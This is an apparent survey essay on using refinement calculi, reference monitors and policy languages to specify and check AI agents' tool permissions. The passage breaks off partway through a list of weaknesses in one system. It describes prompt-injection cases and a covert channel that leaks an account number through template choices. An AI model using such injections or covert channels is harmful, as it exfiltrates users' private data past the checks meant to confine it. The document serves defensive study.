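# Refinement calculi for secure components and the permission scopes of AI agents

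## The basic ideas of agents, permission scopes and refinement

A refinement calculus is a set of rules for turning a specification into a program in small steps, with a proof at each step that the new version keeps every guarantee of the old one. Secure refinement also requires that no step let an observer learn more about secrets than the specification allows. Researchers developed both for conventional software, where a programmer writes the code and can in principle prove properties of it.

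An AI agent is only partly software of that kind. It consists of a language model running in a loop, in which the model chooses calls to software tools, reads their results and chooses again. The tools are ordinary components, programs with a defined interface that send mail, query a database or delete files. The agent's permission scope is the set of calls that are allowed to go through, including their arguments and order. Its reach is everything it can read or affect through any sequence of those calls, which can extend well beyond what the list of calls suggests. For example, an agent that is only allowed to write files to a shared folder also reaches any program that runs files from that folder.

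### From the model to the component

Suppose a user asks an agent to tidy a workspace. The developer has given the model a list of tools, each with a name and a schema describing its arguments. When the model "deletes a file", it only produces structured output containing the name of the delete tool and a path. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states that the model never runs anything on its own. The application extracts the name and arguments, runs the operation, and puts the result into the next request. This repeats for as long as the model's responses contain calls. The model receives the schema and the results, but never the component's code.

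The tool layer is the conventional software that receives a proposed call and either carries it out or refuses it. Papers also call it the harness, framework or containment layer. Its parts can run in different places. For web search, code execution and a few other tools, Anthropic's servers run the operation, and the call usually finishes before the developer's application receives any record of it. A check inside the application then comes too late, so the developer's main control is whether to enable the tool.

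*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) defines a tool invocation as any request through the model that makes an outside system read, write, compute or transmit something. The definition has to be broad enough to include reads. An agent needs permission to read an inbox, for example, and strangers can leave text for the model there.

### Why a prompt does not enforce anything

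The simplest way to limit an agent is to write the limit into its prompt, such as "never delete files". But everything the model reads arrives in the same stream of text, and prompt injection exploits this. Someone hides an instruction in content the agent will read, and the model follows it as if it came from the user. For instance, a job applicant might put invisible text in a CV telling the model to approve the application. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C compares this with SQL injection, an older attack on databases. Programmers could fix SQL injection at its root because database engines treat instructions and data differently. A language model only predicts the next token, and David C doubts that anyone will ever fix prompt injection completely. The post recommends putting deterministic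 safeguards outside the model.

Leong (2026), in *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary*, tested how often a written prohibition fails. The system prompt gave 15 models read-only access and forbade deletion, and the models then encountered false claims of authority to delete. They issued a delete call in 1.76% of 7,500 trials. In an exploratory run with more models, and with prompts written by Claude rather than GPT-5.1, the figure was 3.68%. These rates are low, and 14 of the 15 models in the first test counted as resistant. But they were measured on particular prompts, and an attacker who can send a hundred emails may be content with a 2% success rate.

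Leong also tested a check outside the model that admits only signed records and ties each deletion to a token with a stated scope. It rejected all 750 forged, tampered, replayed or unsigned records. Of the deletion attempts that reached the tool, 83 were aimed outside the token's scope, and none of these removed a file there. Leong calls this a functional test of deterministic checks, which is not evidence about a determined attacker. A deputy with a valid token induced deletions inside the scope in 31 of 42 trials. Such a check enforces the scope as written, even if it doesn't match what the user wanted.

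### The reference monitor

Security engineers call such a check a reference monitor. The idea goes back to a study for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different clearances to share one computer. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, assumed a malicious user who already has legitimate access and can run arbitrary programs, not a bad description of a model under prompt injection. The monitor compares every reference that a program makes to data, devices or other programs with a list of authorized references. Anderson set three requirements:

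- Every reference must go through the monitor. If some programs can skip it, those programs become part of the security apparatus and need the same scrutiny.
- Nobody may be able to tamper with it, since an altered monitor protects nothing.
- It must be small enough for complete analysis and testing, because otherwise nobody can know that it works correctly in all cases.

Anderson used GCOS III, a commercial operating system of the day, to show how easily a system can fail all of these requirements at once. The hardware confined each user's program to its own memory, but the program called on the supervisor for input and output. The supervisor ran mostly with that confinement switched off, so the check did not always apply. Even if the supervisor itself is counted as the monitor, it and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse. The system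 was also open to tampering, since testers had already broken into it several times.

Anderson pictured the authorizations as a table with users and programs down the side, resources along the top and the permitted operations in the cells. Such a table can't fully describe an agent's scope, which also covers the arguments and order of tool calls. In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, Dongol (2026) describes an agent that looks up its user's account number, reads an email and summarises it. The email contains an instruction to fetch a web address that includes the account number. A monitor with memory can withdraw the fetch tool when the agent reads untrusted content, so the injected call fails. A fixed table cannot express that rule, because whether the agent may fetch depends on what it has already read.

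The three requirements also apply to recent agent monitors, which meet them to varying degrees. *Kairos* (2026) describes a monitor on the host's input and output path that observes every event in both directions, which meets the first requirement. It assumes the other two. The monitor in *Agenra* (2026) has a core written in Lean, a language for machine-checked proofs, and the core's functions come with proofs. The compiler, the runtime and much of the surrounding system must still be trusted. For example, if an attacker compromises the address directory that a rule relies on, the monitor will apply the rule correctly and approve mail to the wrong person. The monitor also can't enforce a rule that is missing from the policy.

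Anderson proposed building a monitor by starting with an abstract model of the secure system, developing it into a design in stages, and showing formally at every stage that the design remains faithful to the model. A calculus for this kind of development appeared within the decade.

### Refining a program

Ralph-Johan Back added specifications to Edsger Dijkstra's small programming language in 1978. Carroll Morgan's group at Oxford and Joe Morris at Glasgow later developed closely related versions. *Refinement Calculus* (Back and von Wright, 1997) covers the subject at book length. The notation here follows *On the Refinement Calculus* (Morgan, Robinson and Gardiner, 1988).

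These ideas all build on Dijkstra's weakest precondition. For a program P and a condition R, wp(P, R) describes exactly the starting states from which P is certain to finish with R true. Substitution gives the weakest precondition of an assignment. For example, s := s + t is certain to end with s ≥ 100 exactly when s + t ≥ 100 beforehand.

A specification statement, w : [pre, post], stands for code that nobody has written yet. It means: starting from a state where pre holds, change only the variables w and finish in a state where post holds. Where pre fails, the statement guarantees nothing, not even that the program will stop. It has a weakest precondition of its own (in the simple case where post does not refer to initial values):

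```
wp(w : [pre, post], R)  =  pre ∧ (∀w • post ⇒ R)
```

Specifications and programs are therefore written in the same language, and the same refinement relation applies to both. Q refines P, written P ⊑ Q, when wp(P, R) implies wp(Q, R) for every condition R. This means that Q is certain to achieve anything P is certain to achieve.

The calculus supplies laws so that we don't have to check every R by hand. We can strengthen the postcondition by replacing post with any condition that implies it. We can also split w : [pre, post] into w : [pre, mid] followed by w : [mid, post], where mid is an intermediate condition. An assignment w := E refines w : [pre, post] if pre implies post with E substituted for w.

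As an example, a component sweeps money from a current account c into savings s, with a spare variable t. C and S stand for the opening balances and do not appear in the finished code. The combined balance must stay the same, and at most 10 may remain in the current account.

```
   c,s,t : [c = C ∧ s = S,  c + s = C + S ∧ c ≤ 10]

⊑  (strengthen the postcondition)
   c,s,t : [c = C ∧ s = S,  c = 0 ∧ s = C + S]

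⊑  (split twice)
   c,s,t : [c = C ∧ s = S,          t = C ∧ s = S];
   c,s,t : [t = C ∧ s = S,          t = C ∧ s = S ∧ c = 0];
   c,s,t : [t = C ∧ s = S ∧ c = 0,  c = 0 ∧ s = C + S]

⊑  (one assignment for each)
   t := c;
   c := 0;
   s := s + t
```

The specification left open how much stays in the account, and in the first step the developer made that choice by emptying it. Refinement generally works by removing such freedom. The laws don't stop a developer from going too far. If a developer strengthens a postcondition all the way to "false", the result refines every specification, which is why Morgan and colleagues call it a miracle. No executable code can implement it. Refining one fragment of a program also refines the whole program, so a team can develop the parts separately.

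### Refining a set of traces

Weakest preconditions suit programs that start, compute and finish. A mail server or a tool layer keeps running, and what matters about it is the exchange of messages along the way. A trace is the sequence of events in one run, and one can specify such a component by the set of traces it may produce. Philipps and Rumpe (2014), in *Refinement of Information Flow Architectures*, write β(i) for the set of output histories that a component may produce from the input history i. A component β₂ refines β₁ when

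```
β₂(i) ⊆ β₁(i)   for every input history i
```

A refinement of a component does only what the original could have done. Refinement is transitive, so if each step from specification to implementation is a refinement, the implementation refines the specification. Replacing one component in a network with a refinement of it also refines the whole network.

Trace inclusion preserves every property that one can judge on each trace separately. These include safety properties, such as "no mail to an unlisted address", which require that some bad thing never happens. If every trace in the specification satisfies such a property, the implementation does too, without further proof, because it produces only traces from that set. However, if the specification always allows refusal, a tool layer that refuses every call also refines it, so someone has to check separately that the agent can still do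 its job.

### Secrets

Secrecy is harder, because a single trace does not show whether a secret has leaked. McIver and Morgan (2011), in *Compositional refinement in agent-based security protocols*, use about the smallest example possible: a program with one visible variable v and one hidden variable h. Write r.v.h for the set of visible values that the program r may end with when it starts from v and h. The program satisfies noninterference when

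```
r.v.h₀ = r.v.h₁   for every v and all h₀, h₁
```

so that changing the secret makes no difference to what an observer could see. The program v := 0 passes, since the set is {0} whatever h is. The program v := h mod 2 fails: the set is {0} for even h and {1} for odd h, and anyone who sees v learns the last binary digit of the secret. Now look at one run of the second program, ending with v = 0. It is indistinguishable from a run of the first. Only a comparison between runs with different secrets brings out the leak.

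Noninterference is thus an information-flow property. It limits what an observer can infer, and it is a property of the whole set of traces. Kestrel Institute's *Hyperproperties Project* calls properties of this kind hyperproperties. Trace inclusion does not reliably preserve them, so a correct refinement can make a secure system insecure (the refinement paradox).

Real systems have more than two grades of secrecy. A label on data records how secret the data is, and labels are ordered, like the Confidential, Secret and Top Secret levels of Anderson's Air Force users. Information may flow up the order but not down. Labels can also record how trustworthy data is, and the rule then prevents text in a stranger's email from influencing an action that requires a trusted source.

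Strict noninterference would make many agents useless. Dongol gives the example of a calendar assistant that answers meeting requests with its user's free times, so its replies must depend on private data. The traditional remedy is declassification, which means deliberately and explicitly releasing particular secrets, such as free times but not the names of appointments. Dongol objects that someone must write such a policy for each task, and that the policy describes what the agent may release without isolating what a prompt injection adds.

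### What is there to refine?

A component's code can in principle be derived from a specification step by step. The weights of the model that calls it come from training instead, so they have no such derivation. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) treats the model as an adversary whose only constraint is the typed interface for calls, and does not attempt to verify it. Moon and Varshney (2026), in *Containment Verification*, likewise let the model emit any action of the permitted type (the "arbitrary model" assumption). They prove properties of the framework around the model, which is conventional software and can be refined in the usual way.

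That makes the model part of the environment, much like a user at a keyboard. This seems right for safety properties, since mail to an unlisted address has to pass through the tool layer whoever proposed it, provided there is no other way out. It works less well for secrecy, because the model reads the result of one call and composes the next. Information from a private calendar can reach a permitted recipient through the wording of a permitted message, and the model that chose the wording has no specification. Anyone who claims to have verified what an agent may reach must therefore first decide whether they are refining a component, the tool layer, or the whole system including the model.

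## Writing a permission scope as a specification

A specification of the tool layer must determine whether the layer may carry out each call the model might propose. A list of allowed tools is too coarse for that, because an agent can use the same mail tool to send a customer a receipt or to send a stranger the customer's account number.

### What a scope has to name

Surapani and colleagues describe a tool invocation by seven items: the chain of people and programs whose authority it uses, the operation, its target, its arguments, the delegated scope, the time and session, and a record of where the content behind the call came from. Few scopes need all seven for every tool, but a useful scope nearly always has to name the tools, restrict their arguments, keep some state, constrain the order of calls, and account for data labels.

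Consider a company that opens a ticket for each customer complaint and starts a new session of a support agent for each ticket. The agent has three tools:

- read_ticket(id) returns the text of a ticket.
- read_account(id) returns a customer's record, including the account number.
- send_mail(to, template) sends one of the company's prewritten mails.

The agent may read the account of the customer who opened the ticket, and no other. It may send any of 8 templates to any of 4 addresses, say billing, shipping, the fraud team and an outside repair firm. The templates have no blanks to fill in, so there are 32 possible mails. As a state machine, the scope looks like this:

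```
for each session:  n = the assigned ticket    c = the customer who opened it
                   A = the 4 addresses        T = the 8 templates

state "new"    read_ticket(id)          if id = n                    → "open"

state "open"   read_ticket(id)          if id = n                    → "open"
               read_account(id)         if id = c                    → "open"
               send_mail(to, template)  if to ∈ A and template ∈ T   → "open"

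any other call, in either state: refuse, and stay in the same state
```

The two states express that the agent has to read the ticket before it can do anything else. The tool layer has to look up c, the customer number, in the company's own records, because if it took the number from the text of the ticket, anyone could open a ticket that quotes someone else's number.

This scope doesn't use labels yet. Suppose the company decides that the repair firm should get no mail once the agent has seen account data. A third state, "private", can enforce this. A call to read_account moves the session into that state, where A doesn't include the repair firm. The state then acts as a label on the whole session, recording that the model has read something secret. The label is coarse, since it also blocks mail to the firm that has nothing to do with the account.

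Other rules need numbers. In *What Can Be Enforced?*, Ray (2026) uses the example of an assistant that sends mail and makes payments. One rule caps the total that may go to any recipient in a day, so the machine needs a counter for each recipient and day. Another rule forbids mailing personal information to unapproved recipients. No field of the call shows whether a text contains personal information, so that rule depends on a fallible judge. Ray proves that if such judgments are correct, a deterministic gate that decides before each call can enforce exactly the safety properties that a machine of this kind can track. The gate can't enforce "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation", because it can't take back a payment or make the model confirm it, and refusing the payment would also block runs in which the confirmation would have come.

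### Where the rules come from

The support agent's scope was easy to write because the company already knew what it wanted. In practice, someone has to notice which combinations of calls could do harm, whether a developer writes the scope or a model generates it. In *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026) do this with System-Theoretic Process Analysis, a method borrowed from aviation and other high-risk industries. It looks for accidents caused by interactions between parts, even when no part has failed.

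Their example is a calendar agent that can list events, update events and send email. A user adds an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease, and the appointment clashes with a work meeting. The agent moves the meeting and emails the colleague involved, giving the appointment as the reason. Nobody attacked the agent, and it needed all three tools for its job.

The analysis starts with the people the agent affects, here the user and the other attendees, and what each of them values. Each value implies a possible loss, such as the user's loss of privacy. The developers then work out which behaviour would cause the loss, decide whether it matters enough to address, and write a requirement, such as that notifications contain only essential details. Finally, they restate the requirement as rules about calls and labels. Event details are private from people who aren't attending,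 anything derived from those details is at least as private, and no call to send_email may include data that is private from the email's recipient.

Attendees also value prompt notice, so a rule requires one email to every attendee directly after each update. A tool layer can refuse all other calls until the emails have gone out, but by Ray's result it can't make the model write them.

The privacy rule only works if data carries labels while the agent runs. Doshi and colleagues propose tagging every tool with what it can do, how confidential its data is and how far to trust its output. They would add these tags to the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools. The layer could then block private data from reaching any tool that writes to outside systems, and ask the user when a tag is "unsure". This depends on the tags being written honestly, and they accept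 that an open market of tools would need some further way to establish trust.

To test the idea, they modelled the protocol in Alloy, a tool that searches every run of a model up to a chosen size. Alloy quickly found leaks in the model without the rules, but none once the rules were added. The rules still allowed useful runs, such as rescheduling an event and emailing the participants. The search covers only runs of bounded length in a small model of the system. It also can't detect a hazard that nobody thought of, which is one reason the paper recommends agents with narrow tasks.

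### Guards and preconditions

The conditions in the support agent's state machine are guards, which the tool layer checks itself, refusing the call if they fail. The refinement calculus also allows a condition to be written as the precondition of a specification statement, but that is the wrong place for a permission's conditions.

Let sent be the list of mails sent so far, S its opening value, and + the operation that appends a mail. Suppose a developer specifies send_mail with the permission as a precondition. One of the laws of the calculus allows the developer to weaken a precondition, that is, to replace it with any condition that it implies:

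```
   sent : [sent = S ∧ to ∈ A ∧ template ∈ T,  sent = S + (to, template)]

⊑  (weaken the precondition)
   sent : [sent = S,  sent = S + (to, template)]

⊑  (one assignment)
   sent := sent + (to, template)
```

The finished code can send mail to any address, and its derivation is correct. The original statement places no requirements on the code when its precondition fails, so a version that responded to an unlisted address by mailing out the whole customer database would also be a correct refinement.

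A precondition divides work between a component and its caller, so this isn't a flaw in the calculus. The programmer who calls a square-root routine makes sure that the number isn't negative, so the routine doesn't have to check. This is sensible when someone can prove that the calling code meets the precondition. Here the caller is a language model that may be following an injected instruction, so nobody can guarantee that the address it supplies meets the precondition.

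Z is a notation that describes operations as relations between the state before and the state after. Miarka, Boiten and Derrick (2000), in *Guards, Preconditions, and Refinement in Z*, explain two ways to read an operation's precondition. In the traditional (non-blocking) reading, anything may result when someone applies the operation outside its precondition, while in the alternative (blocking) reading, the operation can't occur there. The same Z text for send_mail could therefore require the tool layer to refuse a call outside the precondition or allow it to do anything, depending on a convention that doesn't appear in the text.

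The convention also affects whether an implementer can add whole tools. Boiten points out in *Introducing extra operations in refinement* that the non-blocking reading allows an implementer to add operations the specification never mentioned, since this only provides functionality that nobody asked for. For a permission scope, this means a "correct" implementation could include an unmentioned delete_account tool. Blocking readings typically rule this out, because no behaviour in the specification matches the new operation.

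Event-B, a later method for developing systems by refinement, makes guards explicit. Its events have parameters, a guard and an action:

```
event send_mail
  any    to, template
  where  to ∈ A ∧ template ∈ T
  then   sent := sent + (to, template)
end
```

*Verifying System-level Security of a Smart Ballot Box* (Dghaym, Hoang and colleagues, 2021) states the proof obligation that the original event must be able to occur whenever the refined event can. Code without the address check fails this test. Strictly, the obligation requires only that *some* permitted arguments exist for the original event, and a companion rule requires the two events' effects to match. The model therefore needs to record each mail in `sent`. Otherwise, a proof could pair a mail to a stranger with a permitted mail to billing.

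A specification with guards still allows a tool layer that refuses every call, because a developer may strengthen the guards at every step. In Boiten's account, Event-B's basic rule against this is that the refined system may get stuck only where the original does, but a layer that permits only read_ticket would satisfy that rule. The blocking version of Z refinement is much stricter and requires every operation to remain available wherever it was before, so the guards can't change and a developer can't narrow a scope.

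Dghaym and colleagues take a middle course, in which the developer marks certain events as "rigid" and must prove that no refinement makes them less available. In their voting system, casting a ballot is rigid, so the box must keep accepting every valid ballot as the design becomes more detailed. For the support agent, one could make mail to billing a separate event and mark it as rigid, so that later versions could drop the repair firm but not billing.

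Preconditions are still useful alongside guards. Miarka and colleagues combine the two so that an operation can refuse some calls and leave its effect unspecified for others. In a tool layer, guards should cover everything that comes from the AI model, while preconditions can cover what trusted software supplies, such as a loaded address list.

### Comparing two scopes

Villa, Kohno and colleagues (2026) observe in *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* that existing proposals for agent permissions are hard to compare because they lack a shared formal foundation. Two scopes are easier to compare when both are state machines over the same tools. Scope A permits no more than scope B if B permits every sequence of calls that A permits. This is trace refinement applied to scopes.

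Suppose the company restricts the support agent to a single address, billing. The new guard, to = billing, implies the old one, to ∈ A, and nothing else has changed, so the new scope refines the old one. If the company instead keeps the four addresses and adds a courier as a fifth, the sequence "read the ticket, mail the courier" is possible only under the new scope, so the new scope does not refine the old one. If the company replaces the repair firm with the courier, neither scope refines the other.

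Reading the list as a precondition reverses the first two answers. Adding a fifth address is then a refinement because it weakens the precondition, and cutting the list to one address is not, because that strengthens it. A team that runs its refinement check under the wrong reading would approve the changes it most wants to catch.

Software already performs such comparisons for ordinary access policies. Cedar is an open-source policy language that Amazon Web Services (AWS) uses in its products. Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues (2024), in *Cedar*, describe its rules. A request names who is asking, the action, the resource and some context. Cedar denies it unless at least one "permit" policy applies and no "forbid" policy does. Leaving the templates and the order of calls aside, a policy for the support agent's mail could read:

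```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"support",
  action == Action::"send_mail",
  resource in Group::"approved"
);
```

*AutoCedar* (2026) treats a policy as the set of requests it permits, so comparing two policies means checking whether one set contains the other. There are far too many requests to list, so Cedar's compiler translates both policies into a logical formula that is true of a request exactly when the new policy allows it and the old one doesn't. An SMT solver, a program that searches for values that make such a formula true, then either finds such a request or proves that none exists. Cedar's designers kept the language simple enough that the translation is exact and the question is always decidable. In their tests, a question took 75.1 milliseconds on average to encode and solve.

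Comparing even short policies can give surprising results. AWS's *Introducing Cedar Analysis* describes a photo-sharing application that lets users view their own photos and any public image. A developer splits this policy into three, one of which forbids access to private files. The comparison tool reports that the new set is less permissive, because owners have lost access to their own private photos. When the developer attaches the privacy condition only to the policy for public images, the tool reports that the new set is equivalent to the original policy.

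A mistake in the translation could make the analyses' results wrong. *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026) therefore proves five of the analyses correct in Lean, and reports that the proofs caught subtle bugs during development. The proofs do not cover the solver, which must still be trusted. A demonstration tool that Torlak built from these analyses found possible authoring mistakes in three of eight example applications.

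AWS offers similar checks for the policies that govern its cloud services. CheckNoNewAccess compares a new policy with an existing one and returns PASS or FAIL. AWS publishes sample reference policies to compare against, and shows how to run the check on every proposed change to a project's code, alongside another check that the policy doesn't grant certain critical permissions. An agent developer could likewise write down the widest acceptable scope once and use the solver to reject any later policy that exceeds it.

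These tools compare decisions about single requests, so they account for the order of an agent's calls only if the application includes it in the request, for example as a field that records whether the agent has read the ticket. The solver doesn't check that the application updates this field correctly, so that has to be verified separately.

The other gap is that the comparison misses changes in data. Cedar keeps group membership outside the policies, and the solver compares two policies on the same data. If an administrator adds the courier to the group "approved", the policy text stays the same and the comparison shows no difference, but the agent now has a fifth address. Writing the addresses into the policy avoids this, but then every new address requires a new policy.

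### Permission and reach

A scope can pass all these checks and still allow the agent to leak the account number. Suppose a prompt injection causes the support agent to read the account and then mail the repair firm nine times, choosing each template according to the digits of the account number. The scope permits the agent to read the account and to send each of the mails. Nine choices among eight templates give about 134 million possible sequences, more than the 100 million eight-digit numbers, so anyone at the repair firm who knows the code can work out the account number from the templates.

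An agent that can send free text doesn't need a code to leak information. *ChainCaps* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) uses the term "permission laundering" for cases where an agent reads a confidential document, summarises it and sends the summary to an outside address, passing every tool's permission check on the way. As a remedy, it gives each value a list of the places where that value may go. A value computed from several others may go only where all of them may go. This covers data that visibly moves from tool to tool, but it wouldn't cover the nine mails, which contain nothing from the account.

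*Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) shows which of these failures a monitor can detect from one run. In the paper's live test, an agent exceeded the user's consent in 22 of 60 runs by combining actions that were each allowed. A guard that tracked the actions' cumulative effect prevented all such violations.

The nine mails are harder to detect because they break a noninterference rule, that mails must not depend on the account number. No single run can violate such a rule, so Pandey and colleagues conclude that a monitor which examines runs one at a time and never raises a false alarm will detect no violations. A company can instead accept false alarms by using the "private" state, which blocks all mail to the repair firm after the agent has read an account.

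Programming-language researchers distinguish *permission* from *authority*. *Object-Capability as a Means of Permission and Authority in Software Systems* (2019) describes permission as the right to access an object directly and invoke its behaviour, and authority as the possibility of invoking that behaviour without a direct link. Mark Miller introduced the terms informally, and Drossopoulou and colleagues later made them precise. Suppose the support agent gets a tool for adding notes to its ticket, and the ticket system forwards new notes to the repair firm. The agent has permission only to add a note, but it has the authority to send the firm any text. A scope lists the agent's permissions, so it may not show everything the agent has the authority to do.

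Authority is especially hard to predict when calls can change permissions. An agent that can share a folder changes what other people and programs may do, and they may grant the agent permissions in return. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman studied such systems in 1976 using a table of rights like Anderson's, plus commands that change it. A command checks for certain rights and, if they are present, adds or removes rights, or creates or deletes users and resources. *Towards a Uniform Framework for Dynamic Analysis of Access Control Models* (2017) describes their "safety" question as whether "some subject ever obtains a specific right with respect to some object".

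They proved that no algorithm can answer this for every system. *Weird Machines in Transport Layer Security* (2026) outlines the proof, which uses the table to build a Turing machine, the standard abstract computer that reads and writes symbols on an endless tape according to a fixed set of rules. Each user in the table represents a cell of the tape, the rights represent the symbols on the tape and the machine's current state, and each command carries out one of the machine's rules. The machine halts exactly when the right that represents its halting state appears in the table. An algorithm for the safety question would therefore determine whether any given Turing machine halts, which Alan Turing had shown no algorithm can do.

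Bishop's textbook on computer security, which the same paper cites, calls the construction artificial. The theorem rules out a single method that works for all systems, but many particular systems are still easy to analyse. The construction also needs commands that create new users without limit, because the tape has no end. With a fixed set of users and resources, the table has finitely many possible states, so a program can in principle check them all. *Safety Analysis in the NGAC Model* (2025) notes that some natural versions of the question are NP-complete, which means they are decidable but probably slow to answer in the worst case. For unrestricted systems, one can still search for a sequence of commands that grants the right. Finding one shows that the right can be granted, but stopping without finding one doesn't show that none exists.

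Ray finds a similar boundary for scopes with counters. If a policy has two counters that can both rise and fall, no algorithm can decide in general even whether the policy is trivial. Spending caps are easier because their counters only rise, and the exact value stops mattering once it passes the cap. For a class of policies that covers caps and revoked access, an algorithm can decide the question with a reasonable amount of memory.

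The support agent is well inside the decidable region. It has two states and 34 permitted calls, none of which changes a permission. A tool that lets the agent grant access to others, or a shell that lets it run arbitrary commands, would make the analysis much harder.

### Permissions spread over several agents

A company may give each of its agents a modest scope and still end up with a dangerous combination. *Safety is Non-Compositional* (2026) proves this with a minimal example in which two capabilities together unlock a forbidden third. If one agent can obtain an approval code and another can obtain a bank token, together they can make a payment that neither could make alone. A graph whose arrows each lead from one capability to another can't show that the payment requires both.

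*A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (Parisel, 2026) proposes a way to look for such combinations before deployment. Under the traditional principle of least privilege, each user or program gets only the permissions its task requires. Parisel argues that one should also count the permissions of every agent that user or program can influence.

The method begins with a tree of the organisation's divisions, departments and resources. For two actions a and b on different resources, Parisel defines a distance, the "blast radius":

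```
d(a, b) = F × 2^−(2D + 1)
```

Here D is the tree depth of the smallest unit that contains both resources, and F is a factor between 1 and 2 that rises with their sensitivity. Actions in the same department are closer together than actions in different divisions.

One agent can influence another if it can write to something the other reads, or if the two can exchange messages. Parisel draws an arrow between them if the actions involved also span at least a distance θ, which the security team chooses. An agent's "effective autonomy" consists of its own actions and those of every agent it can reach by following arrows. This definition deliberately assumes the worst, since an arrow doesn't prove that one agent can command another or that any data has moved between them.

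A system satisfies least autonomy if no agent's effective autonomy exceeds a set budget, someone has explicitly authorised every arrow, and no two agents are in a position to collude. Two agents could collude, for instance, if one can influence the other and the other controls the first one's access, or if influence between them combines access to areas that policy keeps apart.

Parisel works through an example of ten agents, with θ at about 0.219 and a budget of 0.5. One agent submits evidence to a queue, and a second reads the queue and decides what to release to the first. The first also writes reports in Finance and the second reads deployment policies in Engineering, so their actions are far enough apart for the method to draw an arrow between them. The method flags the pair because the first agent can influence the second's decision about its access. Another agent has no contact with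 the rest, but it writes audit evidence and reads legal records in a different division. That agent alone exceeds the budget, with a distance of 0.875.

The calculation takes little compute. For n agents with up to m actions each, it examines at most n(n − 1)m² pairs of actions and then searches the graph in time at most proportional to n³. Because it treats permissions as fixed, it avoids the difficulty that Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman found, but the security team has to repeat the analysis whenever permissions, resources or workflows change.

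The choice of distance is more questionable. Suppose one agent prepares wire transfers, another approves them, and both work only within Treasury. Their actions are at most about 0.014 apart in Parisel's example, far below θ, so the graph has no arrow between the two agents and the method finds no collusion. Yet auditors have long worried about this kind of arrangement. The security team can lower θ to include the pair, but it then has to review and authorise many more arrows.

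## Deriving a narrower scope from a user's request

The support agent's scope permits 34 calls because it has to suit every ticket. Suppose a supervisor assigns the agent a ticket and types, "Ask shipping to trace this parcel." The agent needs only two calls for this, one to read the ticket and one to send shipping the template for a trace. An instruction injected into the ticket could cause the agent to make any of the other 32.

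General-purpose agents have far more permissions than a single task needs. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa (2026), in *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning*, describe a coding assistant connected to GitHub through a common type of access token. The token gives it about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, in every repository its user can open. Summarising the open issues of one repository takes two read-only tools. A malicious instruction in a public repository reportedly steered an agent into reading its user's private repositories and publishing them. A token that could only read the public repository would have prevented this, but it would be too narrow for the user's next task, which might be to fix a failing build and so require writing code.

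Part of the problem is that services grant permissions too coarsely. Sharma, Jiang and colleagues point out in *PAuth* that OAuth, the usual way to let an application act on someone's account, grants the whole transfer operation when the task implies only "transfer $100 to Bob". Agents also don't reliably avoid using permissions they don't need. Parkinson and colleagues cite a test of 544 scenarios in which 6 of 11 agents chose a needlessly powerful tool more than 30% of the time. *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (2026) reports that safety training doesn't ensure better choices.

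### Who writes the narrower scope?

The user knows best what the task is, but few users want to write a policy for each task. Many products instead ask the user to approve each call. According to Parkinson and colleagues, one vendor reported that users of its coding agent approved 93% of these prompts. Many of those requests were probably fine, but a user who approves nearly everything can't be relied on to catch the rare bad one.

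Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, reviewed 21 proposed systems that let individual users set an agent's permissions. They checked whether each system required little work from the user, had a formally grounded policy language and enforced policies deterministically. Roughly half the systems met each criterion, but none fully met all three, and none proved its enforcement code correct. Most systems that require little work from the user rely on a model either to translate a policy from plain English or to predict one from the request.

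The researchers also tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026. These mostly relied on frequent prompts or on a model that reviewed actions with little user control. The Claude chatbot, set to "Needs approval", once created an email draft without asking. When the researchers asked why, it replied that it had inferred permission from their prompt. If that explanation is right, the chatbot derived a scope from their request without showing it to anyone.

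A system can at least write down the derived scope so that conventional software can enforce it. It can derive a new scope from each request, or derive rules once from a company's written policy and apply them to every task.

### From a request to a checked plan

*RefineAct* (Batole, Khomh and Rajan, 2026) applies the refinement calculus directly to an agent's actions. The user's request is the specification, and a plan of tool calls is meant to refine it. The running example is a request to transfer $500 to Alice if the user's balance exceeds $1000.

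A language model first translates the request into a goal in Prolog, a language whose interpreter answers queries by searching for a proof from stored facts and rules. The goal names the operation, its parameters (Alice, 500 and 1000) and a label for the safety condition, `balance_check`. The interpreter checks that the goal is well formed, and the model gets up to three retries if it isn't.

A model then breaks the goal into steps. It relies on the law that splits a specification at an intermediate condition, and on a law for bringing in tools: a tool may replace the sub-goal [pre, post] if running it from any state where pre holds guarantees post. In simplified notation, the plan for the example is:

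```
step 1   check_balance                 requires     nothing

establishes  balance known

step 2   transfer_money(alice, 500)    requires     balance known

establishes  transfer complete

(ask the user first)
```

The model also writes rules about risky inputs. Each rule specifies a tool and a piece of text. If a call to that tool contains the text, the verifier rejects the call or asks the user.

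Finally, the verifier checks each call the agent proposes. If the agent tries the transfer first, "balance known" hasn't been established, so the verifier returns the call with a suggestion to check the balance. Once the agent has done that, the verifier accepts the transfer but prompts the user to confirm it. When the agent declares the task finished, the verifier checks that the last step's postcondition has been established.

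The plan's goal includes the $1000 threshold, but neither step does, so the agent has to check the balance but can make the transfer whatever the balance is. If the account holds $600, the transfer meets the plan's requirements, and only the user's confirmation can stop it. A proof would have exposed the mistake, because after the split, the second step must satisfy the original request from every state in which the balance is known, and a transfer from a balance of $600 doesn't.

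Nobody carries out that proof. Both laws are sound, but RefineAct doesn't check that their conditions hold. Prolog checks the syntax of what the model wrote, and the system takes the model's account of each tool's effect on trust. Three further weaknesses appear while the agent runs:

- The verifier records a step's postcondition when it approves the call, without inspecting the resulting state. Suppose a plan deletes a folder only after backing it up. If the backup fails, the verifier may still count it as done and let the deletion through.
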